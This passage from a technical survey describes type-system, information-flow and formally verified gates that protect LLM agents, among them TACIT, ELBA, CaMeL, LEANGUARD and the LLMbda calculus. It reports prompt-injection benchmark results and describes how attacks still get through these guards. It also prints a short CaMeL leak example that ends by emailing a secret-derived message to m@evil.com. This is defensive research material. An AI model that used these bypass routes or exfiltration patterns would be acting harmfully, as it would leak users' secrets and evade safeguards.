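The braces contain the capture set, and `Unit` is the result type of code that returns no useful value. The second function has an empty set, which makes it pure. It can compute a result but cannot write to a file, contact a server or print anything. A function type with a smaller capture set is a subtype of the same type with a larger one, so a program can pass a pure function where one that may use `f` is expected, but not the other way round.

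Agents get capabilities for a limited stretch of code:

```
requestFileSystem("/data") { fs => ... }
```

Between the braces, the agent's code can use `fs` to reach files under `/data`. To keep this access after the block ends, the code might return a function that reads a file later. That function would have `fs` in its capture set, but the type of the block's result has to make sense outside the block, where `fs` does not exist, so the compiler rejects the code. TACIT handles network hosts and shell commands the same way, with a list of permitted ones for each block. The compiler does not have the values needed to check whether a given path is really under `/data`, so the library checks this at run time.

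Secret files arrive in a wrapper, of which this is the central part:

```
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The agent can apply a function to the contents with `map`, but the plain arrow in `T -> U` admits only pure functions, and the result is again in a wrapper. If `contract` holds a secret document, the compiler treats two attempts to use it as follows:

```
contract.map(text => text.length)                // accepted: Classified[Int]
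contract.map(text => { f.write(text); text })    // rejected: captures f
```

If the agent prints a wrapped value, the user's terminal shows the contents, but the model receives only `Classified(****)`. For tasks that require understanding the text, such as summarising it, the agent can pass the wrapped document to a second language model that the company runs itself and trusts. Its answer is also wrapped. The cloud model can therefore organise the whole comparison without reading the contracts or the summary.

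A sandbox, which confines a program to certain files and network addresses, cannot prevent this leak. The agent has permission to read the contract and to contact the cloud model, so it can pass data from the first to the second without leaving the sandbox.

The guarantee holds only if agent code cannot bypass capture checking. TACIT compiles this code in a "safe mode" that forbids unchecked type conversions and reflection, which lets a program look up and call code by name while it runs. Exceptions could also leak secrets, so the runtime catches them and turns them into ordinary values. Machine-checked soundness proofs exist for the core of capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues have not proved that safe mode as a whole delivers what they promise. About 1,000 lines of library code must also be correct, because that code can use features that safe mode forbids.

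### Tests of TACIT

For their main test, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a directory of passwords, keys and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections each and added 11 requests in which the user asked for secrets outright or under a pretext. They ran the resulting 131 trials on each model once with the wrapper ("classified" mode) and once without.

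| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Trials without a leak, classified mode | 100% | 100% |
| Trials without a leak, unclassified mode | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| Ordinary tasks completed, classified mode | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Ordinary tasks completed, unclassified mode | 83.3% | 88.3% |

The perfect scores follow from the design, so the test mainly confirms that the implementation matches it. The unclassified runs show how much the wrapper was needed. Prompt injections caused no leaks with Claude and 3 in 120 trials with MiniMax. Malicious users succeeded more often, 2 times out of 11 against Claude and 8 out of 11 against MiniMax. Claude also completed tasks much more often in classified mode, but probably not because of types. Without the wrapper, it often ran out of time or turns, or stopped to warn the user about an injection, which the team suspects is an artefact of the set-up.

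Writing typed programs did not noticeably reduce the agents' performance. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models' success rates were 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues from GitHub, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent without. The compiler rejected 0.32 to 7.93 per cent of the programs in the τ²-bench runs, depending on the model and the domain. Models usually fixed these on the first or second attempt.

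LACUNA, which comes from the same group, gave less favourable results. On τ²-bench, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0 per cent of tasks with LACUNA and 90.0 per cent with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call this "on par", which understates the 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4 per cent of the model's code in the retail conversations. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, rejections reached 89 per cent in one domain, and the agent made no progress on most turns. Rejected code never ran, so a model that writes poor code solves fewer tasks and takes longer but is no less safe. Stronger models have less trouble. In the ELBA tests, which used models such as Claude Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 5, agents needed only 0.13 retries per run, although they had to write Haskell.

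### ELBA: effect types as safety policies

Haskell's types show whether a computation has effects. A computation of type `Int` has none, while one that accesses files or the network has a type marked `IO`. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) illustrates this with an AI calculator open to anyone on the internet. If a visitor asks it to delete the server's files and then compute a factorial, the model may well write a program that does both. The compiler rejects that program because it has an `IO` type and the calculator requires `Int`.

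Most agents need some effects. In ELBA, the developer defines a new effect type with only the permitted operations and requires the agent's program to have that type. This is close to what Omar and colleagues planned for Bastion, but ELBA is working software. The main example is an agent that compiles bibliographies and may write only entries that it has fetched from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. In simplified form, its interface is:

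```
dblpSearch      : String → BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    : DOI → BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile : Trusted Bib → BibIO ()
```

A DOI is a publication's identifier, and the square brackets stand for a list. `BibIO` is the effect type, and the agent's whole program must have the type `BibIO ()`, so it can combine these three operations with any computation that has no effects. `Trusted Bib` is an abstract type, so code outside the library cannot construct a value of it and can only get one by fetching it from DBLP. The agent can sort the entries, filter them by year or pick the earliest, but it cannot write an entry it made up.

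A developer could get the same guarantee from ordinary tools by merging the last two operations into one that both fetches and writes an entry. But then the agent could not use code to find the earliest paper, and the model would have to read the entries one by one.

The team compared the two approaches on 100 bibliographies, using Sonnet 5 for both. An agent with a web search tool got the authors, year or DOI wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations, while the ELBA agent made no such errors in 925. The types guarantee only that each entry comes from DBLP, so a genuine paper on the wrong topic also passes the type check.

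An agent often has to look at something before it can decide what to do next. In ELBA, the generated program can call `agent` again and pass on what it has found. For example, if the bibliography agent needs to see the first search result before it settles on keywords, it can write a program that runs the search and hands the result to a sub-agent. Because this second call is inside a `BibIO` program, Haskell infers the type `BibIO ()` for it too, and the sub-agent has the same three operations as its parent. The parent can tighten the restriction by asking for a plain `String`, which rules out all effects, but it cannot loosen it, because a call of type `IO ()` does not type-check inside a `BibIO` program.

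Zhou and colleagues prove that this works in general. Take any property of tool calls that holds for every well-typed program in the host language. It then also holds for every well-typed program that contains agent calls. The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function from prompts to programs and limits how deeply agents may call further agents:

- With a limit of zero, an agent call returns nothing.
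- With a limit of n + 1, the call can be replaced by an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the reply against the required type and runs it if it passes. Any agent calls in the reply have a limit of at most n, so the same replacement already works for them.
- After all replacements, the program makes the same tool calls as before. It is now an ordinary well-typed program of the host language, so it has the property.

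The argument does not depend on what the model was trained to do or what it has read. But the theorem only passes on guarantees the host language already gives. If a developer puts a dangerous operation into `BibIO`, every sub-agent inherits it.

### Information flow

If an agent is allowed both to read private data and to send messages, a list of permitted operations cannot control which data end up in which message, or whose text influenced the decision to send it. Information-flow control tracks this by attaching labels to data and combining the labels whenever a program combines the data.

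A confidentiality label records who may read something, and an integrity label records whether it comes from a trusted source. If a program computes z from x and y, the cautious rule is:

```
readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
trusted(z) = trusted(x) ∧ trusted(y)
```

The symbol ∩ keeps only the people in both sets. For example, if Ann, Ben and Cara may read a sales report and Ben, Cara and Dan may read a contract, only Ben and Cara may read a summary of both. If either document comes from an untrusted source, the summary is untrusted too.

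The system then checks the labels against a policy before each tool call. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) uses two conditions that cover most practical cases. The agent may take an action with consequences, such as a payment, only if it decided on the action in a trusted context, before any untrusted text could influence it. It may call a tool that sends data out only if it meets this same condition or if every recipient is permitted to read the data. The tainted sessions in Fonseca's AeonBox are a simple version of the same idea.

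Labels accumulate restrictions, so once an agent has read a single untrusted email, everything it decides afterwards counts as untrusted, and it can no longer make payments on its own. A common remedy, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023, is to split the agent into two models. One makes the decisions and never receives untrusted text, while the other processes that text but has no tools.

### Programs fixed before the agent reads any data

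CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, turns Willison's pattern into a complete system. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes CaMeL's parts. A planning model sees only the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model reads emails, web pages and other outside text, and extracts what the program needs. Its answers go into variables whose contents the planning model never sees.

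Suppose the user asks the agent to find Bob's email address in a chat channel and send him the time of a meeting. The plan has three steps: read the channel, have the quarantined model extract the address, and send the message. An attacker who posts in the channel cannot add a fourth step, because the plan was complete before the agent read the post, but he may still be able to change the address the model extracts. CaMeL's interpreter therefore records the sources and permitted readers of every value, and a policy written in Python uses that record to allow or deny each tool call.

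Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* relies on the same separation and adds a proof before the program runs. The model produces a plan as structured data, and a verifier checks it against the safety policy before any step is executed. One of his policies forbids any path from the contents of fetched emails to the body of a message addressed outside the company. An ordinary program-analysis tool can search a plan for such a path. The check is the same whether the forbidden step came from a malicious user or a misleading tool description.

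Meijer's second example concerns correctness. A user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes a one-step plan that deletes `*.txt`, meaning every text file. If the specification requires only that the two files be gone afterwards, the verifier accepts the plan. The remedy is a frame condition, which states what must stay the same:

```
∀file. file ∉ {foo.txt, bar.txt}  ⇒  (file ∈ after ⇔ file ∈ before)
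```

The double arrow means "exactly when", and `before` and `after` are the sets of files at the start and the end. Meijer attaches a condition of this kind to the deletion tool. Without it, the verifier could not rule out that deleting `foo.txt` removes other files. But the one-step plan fails only if the task has its own frame condition, as it does above. As in the taxi problem, a goal does not constrain anything it leaves out.

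Meijer had not measured how planning everything in advance affects an agent's performance, though he expected it to help the model reason. He also wants the agent to supply a formal proof that its plan is safe, a proposal he repeated in a 2026 talk, *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls*.

A plan completed before the agent reads anything cannot fully adapt to what the agent finds. In CaMeL, data can determine which of the planner's existing branches runs, but cannot add a new one. If a user asks an agent to work through a to-do list in an email, the planner must write the plan without seeing the list. ELBA lets the agent read first and then write its next program, and uses labels to restrict what that program may do. The labels come from LIO, an established Haskell library for information flow, which checks them while the program runs. The all-or-nothing guarantee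 therefore covers only type errors, and a well-typed ELBA program can still stop halfway because of a label violation, after completing its earlier steps.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) shows that agents that divide work among themselves can be open to attack even if CaMeL protects each one. An agent treats its caller's message as a trusted instruction, but the message may contain untrusted data that has lost its label. In the paper's tests, attacks succeeded in 12.9 per cent of trials without CaMeL, 0.2 per cent with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and none with a protocol that sends instructions and data through different channels. The 0.2 per cent rate is low, but it means that the guarantee no longer holds. ELBA avoids the problem within one application because a sub-agent's program runs as part of its parent's, with the same type and labels.

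### Checking the order of actions

CaMeL checks its policies against one tool call at a time, so they cannot express that an incident report, once opened, must eventually be closed. CaMeLoT also checks the entire plan before running it. It translates the plan into a finite graph of states and passes the graph to a model checker, a program that examines every path through it. The user can require a safety property, such as never disconnecting a computer without prior approval, or a liveness property, such as eventually closing every open report. If a path violates the property, the planner receives that path and revises the plan. Nikolaou and colleagues model a loop as a free choice between continuing and stopping after each round. This covers any number of rounds, but it also causes the checker to reject some safe plans.

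*ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) puts rules about the order of actions into the types of a new language for agents. A type can require that a request for approval come before any request to change a code repository. The compiler verifies this where it can and leaves the remaining paths to a run-time monitor. With ordinary effect types, an agent that skips the approval can look harmless in a dry run, because the test code intercepts and discards each write, which removes it from the program's effect type. ETAS keeps a separate record of everything the program requested, including intercepted requests, so the compiler still finds the missing approval.

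The rule covers only the order of requests, so a program that asks for approval, receives a "no" and writes anyway still satisfies it. In the team's example, the program tests the answer with an ordinary `if`, and the host system is supposed to check consent again before it changes any files.

### The price in completed tasks

Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on the 21 Slack tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants prompt injections in the data that agents read. Each task was paired with 5 attacks, giving 105 combinations. All four models resisted every attack even without ELBA's policies, so to find out what the policies contribute, the team simulated a worst case in which any sub-agent that encounters a planted instruction obeys it. They ran each combination seven times, for 735 trials per model.

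| Model | Injections resisted, no policies | Injections resisted, with policies | Tasks completed, no policies | Tasks completed, with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT-5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The policies stopped every injection, but the agents could no longer complete 33 to 44 per cent of the tasks they had completed without them. The cause is the cautious treatment of labels. When an agent reads untrusted data, its privileges drop to those of the data's source, but many legitimate tasks require it to read a web page or a message and then act.

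Policies reduced CaMeL's task completion even more. When there was no attack, it completed 13 to 17 of the 21 Slack tasks without policies and only 4 to 6 with them. ELBA completed 14 to 18 without policies and 8 to 10 with them, but took about three times as long as CaMeL. This is a small set of tasks, but *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which presents an agent language with machine-checked proofs about information flow, also reports that CaMeL's completion rate halves on AgentDojo's banking tasks when its policies are on.

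TACIT's results on AgentDojo vary widely. With o4-mini-high, it completed 53 per cent of the office tasks, against 81 per cent for CaMeL. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, it completed 64 per cent of the travel tasks, against 1 per cent for CaMeL. In 1,926 trials, the benchmark counted one attack on TACIT as successful. In that trial, the agent quoted hotel reviews that recommended the attacker's hotel but booked the one the user wanted. The type system did not block the quotes because the policy allowed the agent to show the user public reviews.

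Kolluri and colleagues argue that it is fairer to judge a protected agent instead by how many human approvals it needs to finish the same work. Companies rarely let an unprotected agent act entirely on its own; they have a person approve risky actions. The benchmarks, however, compare a protected agent that gets no human help with an unprotected one that never asks for approval. When approvals were counted, even basic information-flow control reduced them by a factor of up to 1.5 with no loss of completed tasks, because the system could prove that some actions were safe without asking.

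The paper's own agent, Prudentia, takes the policies into account when it plans, which reduced approvals further. It can also ask the user to vouch for a piece of data. If a to-do list in an email requires ten sensitive actions, the user can approve the email once instead of approving each action. This is convenient, but it makes the user responsible for checking the data. A user who vouches for a long email and overlooks a planted instruction switches off the protection for everything that follows from that email.

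### Harm that a well-typed program can still do

An attacker does not need to break the type system if the agent already has the permissions the attack requires. In the AgentDojo tests of LACUNA, 7 of 949 attacks succeeded with Gemini 2.5 Pro and 1 of 949 with o4-mini-high. Zhao and colleagues connect these cases with a limit they acknowledge, which is that the compiler does not stop a manipulated model from misusing a capability the task requires. For example, an agent whose job is to send emails can send the wrong one. The compiler enforces the permissions a developer chooses for each task, so the protection is only as strict as those permissions.

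Policies depend on the people who write them in the same way. CaMeL's Python policies can express finer distinctions than a comparison of labels can, but *SPA* (2026), another information-flow system for agents, notes that the guarantee then depends on every policy being correct and complete.

Secrets can also leak through channels that types do not track. A pure function cannot send data, but its running time can depend on the first letter of a secret, so anyone who measures the delay learns something about the secret. The guarantee from Odersky and colleagues does not cover such timing channels or leaks through whether a program finishes.

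External commands are a larger practical gap. When an agent starts another program, such as a version-control tool, that program runs outside Scala, so the compiler can't check what it does. The only remaining control is the list of permitted commands. Odersky and colleagues recommend keeping that list short and also running the agent in a sandbox. Coding agents work largely through such commands, so the gap affects one of the most common uses of agents. All of these systems also depend on the compiler itself, and a bug in it could let a forbidden program through.

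### From capabilities to refinements

No type in TACIT, ELBA or LACUNA limits a number. The types determine whether an agent can reach the payment tool and what data it can send there, but the tool accepts any integer unless its own code checks the amount. The `spend` function needed refinement types to limit the amount, but so far the systems that check agents' programs mainly use capabilities and effects.

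Zhou and colleagues name refinement types among the extensions that would suit ELBA, together with linear types for permissions that an agent may use only once. Zhao and colleagues describe the step more concretely, since Bovel and colleagues have already built refinements into the Scala compiler. The type in an `agent` call could then carry a condition:

```
agent[{v: Int with 0 <= v && v <= b}]("choose how much of the invoice to pay now")
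```

The model would have to write code whose result provably lies between 0 and the balance b. As with `spend`, an amount from an email would first need a run-time test, and the compiler would return an error to the model if the test was missing. The condition would not stop the model from paying the whole balance to the wrong supplier.

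## Proving the action interface safe for every model output

TACIT and ELBA check every program an agent writes, but many agents write no programs and only request one tool call after another. For these agents, engineers can prove that the surrounding software is safe without analysing the model. They define a type of actions and assume that the model may return any value of that type at any moment. Then they prove once, before deployment, that the software never turns those values into a forbidden effect.

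### A payment limit, proved by induction

Suppose an agent can take three kinds of action:

```
Action = Read | Send(amount : nat) | Stop
```

The type `nat` contains the whole numbers from zero upwards. The software keeps a counter called `sent`, which starts at 0, and handles the actions like this:

```
Read     → show the model its inbox
Send(x)  → if sent + x ≤ 100 then pay x and set sent to sent + x
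           else do nothing
Stop     → end the session
```

The safety policy is that payments never exceed 100 in total. Let `total` be the sum of the payments that have actually left the account. The invariant to prove is:

```
total = sent  ∧  sent ≤ 100
```

- At the start, both numbers are 0.
- `Read` and `Stop` change neither number.
- If `sent + x` is more than 100, `Send(x)` changes neither number.
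- Otherwise `Send(x)` raises both numbers by x. They stay equal, and the test has just established that the new value is at most 100.

By induction, the invariant holds after any number of actions. It needs both `sent ≤ 100` and `total = sent`. If a programmer forgot to update the counter, `sent ≤ 100` would stay true while the agent paid out without limit, but `total = sent` would fail at the first payment. The type `nat` rules out negative payments, as the condition 0 ≤ x does for `spend`.

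An agent gains nothing by splitting a large payment into small ones, since the counter adds them up. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested a solver-based gate against this and other tactics in a money-transfer task. No attack succeeded, the gate blocked no legitimate transfer, and its core check took 0.44 milliseconds on average.

So far the action has no recipient. If we change it to `Send(to, amount)`, the proof still holds, because no step uses `to`. The agent can therefore start with `Send(Mallory, 100)`, which passes the test because 0 + 100 ≤ 100. The invariant holds throughout, but when the agent later tries to pay Alice the 100 she is owed, the software refuses because the budget is spent.

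The remedy is to include the recipient in the policy. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) does this for an agent that has to send Alice the public part of a report once. The application names one directory lookup as the authority for her address, and the gate compares the actual recipient with the stored result of that lookup. This check stops the agent from substituting another address, but the gate will approve a wrong address if someone has tampered with the directory. The gate also deducts each attempt from the agent's quota before the mail tool runs, so failed attempts count. The researchers found that the gate let the agent send Alice any public text, because their first policy did not require the text to come from the report.

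### Containment verification

The proof above covers a design of a few lines, but a real agent runs on a larger program, and someone has to show that this program follows the design. Containment verification, a method introduced in 2026, does this with two transition systems. A transition system consists of states, including a starting state, and the steps that can follow from each state. Here, each step records the action the model returned and the event the software produced, such as a payment or a file read.

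The abstract system is a short specification, and the concrete system describes the implementation in detail. Both have the same set of actions and define a step for every action in every state, even if that step only rejects the action. The model is a "havoc oracle", which means it may return any value of the action type at each step.

The concrete system refines the abstract one if everything it does matches something the abstract one could do. This kind of refinement has nothing to do with refinement types. A refinement type attaches a condition to a type, whereas this refinement is a relation between two systems, one of which implements the other. To establish it, an engineer defines which concrete states and events correspond to which abstract ones, and proves three conditions:

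1. The two starting states correspond.
2. Whenever two states correspond and the concrete system takes a step on some action, the abstract system can take a step on the same action, with a corresponding event, to a corresponding state.
3. Whenever two steps match in this way and the abstract step obeys the abstract policy, the concrete step obeys the concrete policy.

Suppose the specification uses the `sent` counter, but the implementation stores `remaining`, which starts at 100. The implementation pays x if x ≤ `remaining`, then subtracts x from `remaining`. Two states correspond if `sent + remaining = 100`, which is true at the start because `sent` is 0. If the states correspond when the model returns `Send(x)`, the tests `sent + x ≤ 100` and `x ≤ remaining` give the same result, so both systems pay or neither does. A payment raises `sent` by x and lowers `remaining` by x, so the states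 still correspond. If `sent` is at most 100, then `remaining` is at least 0, so the account is not overdrawn.

The soundness theorem has two premises:

- The abstract system obeys its policy in every run, whatever actions it receives.
- The concrete system refines the abstract one.

It follows that the concrete system obeys its own policy at every step, whatever model is connected to it.

The proof is another induction, along any run of the concrete system with any model. The starting states correspond, so condition 2 gives an abstract step that matches the first concrete step. The resulting states also correspond, so condition 2 applies again, and so on along the run. This builds an abstract run with exactly the same actions. The first premise covers every sequence of actions, so every step of this abstract run obeys the policy. Condition 3 then implies that the concrete steps obey it too.

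The guarantee does not depend on the model's training. Training changes which sequences of actions a model is likely to return, but the theorem holds for all of them, and neither premise involves the model's weights, prompt or intentions. A more capable model may be better at finding the most harmful sequence that the policy permits. It cannot make the verified software produce a forbidden event, although it might find a way to cause effects that bypass the interface.

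The developers of the method proved the theorem in Dafny and applied it to PocketFlow, a framework for building agents that advertises itself as 100 lines long. A PocketFlow agent is a graph of nodes, and a loop moves from node to node according to the action each one returns. The verified policy has three rules:

- The agent reads files only inside its workspace.
- It calls only tools on an approved list.
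- It takes no more than a fixed number of steps.

The proof consists of six Dafny modules. Two of its lemmas are specific to PocketFlow, one for the starting state and one for a single step. Claude models wrote the specifications and proofs for two example agents, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents, and further checks screened out empty specifications. Each run of this process used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens, and Dafny took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds to verify each path through the loop. Dafny then compiled the verified code to Python.

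This result is small because the interface has only four kinds of action. Larger frameworks such as LangChain have many more, and each kind adds cases to the proof. The guarantee also depends on how narrow the actions are. An action that runs shell commands leaves the same gap as in TACIT.

### A typed envelope for agent skills

The refinement-typed function `dispatch`, which accepts a tool-call envelope e only if `permission(e) ∈ D`, is another gate of this kind. Metere designed it for agent skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. If the surrounding program type-checks and every route to an outside service goes through `dispatch`, no envelope with an undeclared permission reaches a service, whatever the model returns. The type checker does not establish that every route goes through `dispatch`, so someone has to check this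 by inspecting the program or analysing it separately.

Metere also searches sequences of calls for a session in which something in the outside world changes without a matching approval in the log. The search treats each envelope only as one of the |D| declared permissions or as "undeclared", so there are |D| + 1 possibilities per call and (|D| + 1)^K sequences of K calls. With 10 permissions and 8 calls, there are 11⁸ = 214,358,881 sequences, few enough for a computer to check them all.

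The number of sequences grows quickly, however. The paper's worked example has three permissions and 100 calls, which gives 4¹⁰⁰, or about 1.6 × 10⁶⁰ sequences. Metere reports that an SMT solver found no violation among them, but the published code uses no solver and enumerates the sequences one by one, which is impossible at that length. The induction for `Send` avoids this problem by checking a single step from an arbitrary permitted state, so it covers sessions of any length.

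The work is a single-author paper from Metere Consulting, and its code guarantees less than its theorems do. The published `dispatch` is a JavaScript function that throws an error if the permission is undeclared. This is a reasonable run-time test, but no type checker has proved anything about the function. The tool that checks a skill's scripts searches their text for known patterns, so it can miss an effect written in an unusual way.

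Metere also argues that a hostile model can leak at most log₂(|D| + 1) bits through each envelope, which is about 3.5 bits for 10 permissions. This bound counts only which permission the envelope uses and ignores its arguments. The body of a permitted email, for example, can contain an entire confidential document.

### Policies that depend on history

The `sent` counter is a very simple record of the past. Many rules need more, such as "look up a flight before cancelling it". Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LEANGUARD*, built a gate whose policies can refer to the agent's earlier actions, and wrote it in Lean. It allows a tool call only if all of the following hold:

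- At least one permit covers the call.
- Every requirement that applies to the call is met.
- No prohibition applies.
- The gate was able to evaluate all of these conditions without an error.

The last condition prevents the gate from treating missing data as permission. For instance, if the database has no status for an order, the gate must not treat the order as "has not been shipped". The team separately defined in temporal logic what it means for a history to satisfy a policy, and proved that the gate's code agrees with that definition for every history. Lean checks the proof when a developer builds the policy, so the gate doesn't need to prove anything while the agent runs.

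The team tested five Qwen models on τ²-bench. Without the gate, the agents executed at least 33 calls that the policy forbids; with it, they executed none, as the design guarantees. When the gate's refusals included an explanation for the agent, the share of tasks completed fell from 72.7 to 70.9 per cent, which is not a significant change.

A second test, on the prompt-injection benchmark DTap, shows how much the loss in task completion depends on the policy. The agents were allowed to read data but not change it. The success rate of direct attacks fell from 57.9 to 5.9 per cent, but the share of ordinary tasks the agents completed also fell, from 53.1 to 12.5 per cent.

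A gate can also propose an alternative to a forbidden call. If an agent has spent 60 of a budget of 100 and tries to spend 70, a search in Lean can find and prove that 40 would be allowed, provided the task permits a smaller amount. When Sankar and colleagues replayed 252 calls that the gate had refused because of their arguments, the search repaired 88 of them. The live system does not use this search yet.

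Coding agents usually have a shell, which is a broad interface. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin et al., 2026) narrows it by working out what each command does. Tether runs the command on a disposable layer over the file system, holds back its network requests and records its system calls (its requests to the operating system). It translates these calls into 11 kinds of typed action, such as `read`, `copy` and `uploadNet`. If the policy allows every action, Tether makes the changes permanent; otherwise, it discards them.

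Suppose an agent uploads a public report, copies a confidential inventory over it and then uploads the file again. The two upload commands are identical, but the copy has changed the file's label to sensitive, so Tether blocks the second upload. Because the policy is a Lean definition, its writer can prove by induction that an invariant holds for action sequences of any length, such as that the agent never uses the network after reading a sensitive file. The proof doesn't cover the translation from system calls to typed actions, which the team tested with fuzzing, a method that feeds a program large numbers of generated inputs.

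Developers keep changing an agent's permissions, and when permissions can run out, even a more generous policy can do damage. Shivakumar and colleagues give the example of an agent that may delete file A once and file B once. The gate uses the first permission on its list that fits:

| | First permission | Second permission | Delete A, then B | Delete A twice |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before the change | B, once | A, once | Allowed | Refused |
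| After the change | A or B, once | A, once | Refused | Allowed |

After the change, deleting A uses up the first permission, and the second does not cover B. The wider policy therefore blocks the intended work and allows something that was forbidden. To catch such losses, the team checks that every call allowed by the old permissions has a match under the new ones, and that the two sets of counters still correspond afterwards. Containment verification uses the same kind of step-by-step matching. Out of 51 test revisions, the check approved all 21 that preserved the existing workflows and none of the 30 that broke one. An approved revision can still be unsafe. For example, raising a quota from one email to two preserves every workflow but also permits a second email.

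### Secrets and the LLMbda calculus

A payment limit is a condition on a single run, but secrecy requires comparing runs, because an output reveals a secret only if a different secret would have changed the output or its probability. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) proves a property of this kind for the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language for agents. Programs in the language can send prompts to a model, copy or clear the conversation, and run code that the model returns. Every value has a label, and so does the conversation.

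Label tracking without such a proof can go wrong in subtle ways. The paper describes a leak in CaMeL that works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program assigns to it inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and secret. The program then skips the assignment to `rich`, which stays true and public, so CaMeL allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email is sent. The attacker can tell the two cases apart, although no secret value reached the email.

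In the LLMbda calculus, the conversation is the only thing a program can modify. The interpreter stops the program if a branch that depends on a secret tries to write to a public conversation.

The main theorem compares two starting points that differ only in their secrets. Model replies are random, so each starting point leads to a probability distribution over outputs. By the theorem, the secrets do not change the distribution of public outputs, except possibly through whether the program finishes. If the program always finishes, the two distributions are identical. If it sometimes stops with an error or runs forever, the secrets may affect how often that happens.

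The exact condition is that a single assignment of probabilities to public outputs, adding up to at most 1, is at least as high as both distributions for every output. Suppose a program prints "done" with probability 0.6 for one secret and 0.9 for another, and otherwise never finishes. Assigning 0.9 to "done" covers both distributions, so the theorem allows this. A program that printed "yes" with probability 0.7 for one secret and "no" with probability 0.7 for the other would need an assignment adding up to at least 1.4, so no program in the calculus can behave this way.

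To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs that skips any computation once its label becomes secret and substitutes a dummy value. This version never uses the secrets, so it gives the same distribution for both starting points. Skipping can only make a program finish more often, so this distribution is at least as high as each of the originals and serves as the common assignment. Lean checked the proof, and the interpreter that calls the model is a Lean program covered by the theorems.

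This theorem also doesn't depend on how the model was trained. It holds for any rule that assigns probabilities to the model's replies, whatever code those replies contain. But the rule may use only the current conversation. If a provider let the model remember other conversations, a secret could travel through that memory without a label.

The exception for termination allows a small leak, because an attacker may learn something from whether a run stopped. CaMeL made this leak larger with an untracked loop that restarted failed runs, so an attacker could extract a secret one bit at a time. Agents in the LLMbda calculus run their retry loops inside the language, where the labels still apply.

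Agents often have to act on untrusted data, so the calculus has an `endorse` operation that marks a value as trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsing data never exposes secrets, but endorsing can still let an attacker choose what the agent does. In 1,296 attacked runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks, two attacks succeeded, both on the same task. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file. Without `endorse`, the system blocked this attack, but agents completed fewer ordinary tasks, 30 instead of 36 out of 48 with one model and 26 instead of 31 with another.

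### Which properties a gate can enforce

Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, works out what a gate can enforce if it allows or blocks each action before it happens and never interferes with an agent that is following the policy. Such a gate can enforce only safety properties, and only those whose violations it can detect from the actions so far. A daily cap on transfers to each recipient meets both conditions, as does a rule that the agent sends nothing after the user revokes its access.

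A gate cannot enforce the policy "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation." If it allows a proposed payment, the confirmation may never come, and nobody can take the payment back. If it blocks the payment, it may stop an agent that would have sent the confirmation. A designer can instead require the confirmation before the payment, which a gate can enforce, but that is a different policy.

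"Never email personal information to an unapproved recipient" is a safety property, but judging whether a text contains personal information requires interpretation. In practice a classifier has to label the text, and classifiers make mistakes. The gate can therefore guarantee only that text the classifier flags as containing personal information is never emailed to an unapproved recipient.

Truthfulness and good judgment are even harder to guarantee, because a gate's decision depends only on the actions, their arguments and the recorded state. Suppose an agent pays Alice 100 for a genuine invoice on one occasion and for an identical-looking forgery on another. The gate has the same record both times, so it must make the same decision, although only the first payment is correct. Likewise, the sentence "your parcel has arrived" has the same characters whether it is true or false, so a gate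 can check it only against a record, as `confirmRefund` does for refunds.

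## Verified controllers for physical systems

A payment gate can refuse an action and leave the account unchanged, but a train moving at 20 m/s keeps rolling when its software refuses a command. A safety proof for a physical system therefore has to cover the motion between decisions, and a gate that forbids one action has to supply another. Control engineers worked on both problems long before language models could call tools. They developed the proved envelope, a set of actions proved safe from which an untrusted controller can choose freely.

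### Simplex and shields

An early version is the Simplex architecture, which Seto, Krogh and colleagues described in 1998 as a way to upgrade control software while a machine is running. It pairs a new controller that performs well but is hard to analyse with a simple, trusted one. A monitor switches to the simple controller before the machine leaves the region from which that controller can recover. This works without an analysis of the new controller, provided the region is correct.

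Reinforcement learning made the idea more pressing, because a learner finds out which actions earn a high reward by trying them, including dangerous ones. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (2017) describes a shield that computes, at every step, which actions are compatible with a safety property. The learner then picks one of them. Other shields act after the learner has chosen and replace an unsafe action with a fallback. In both arrangements, safety does not depend on whether or how quickly the learner improves.

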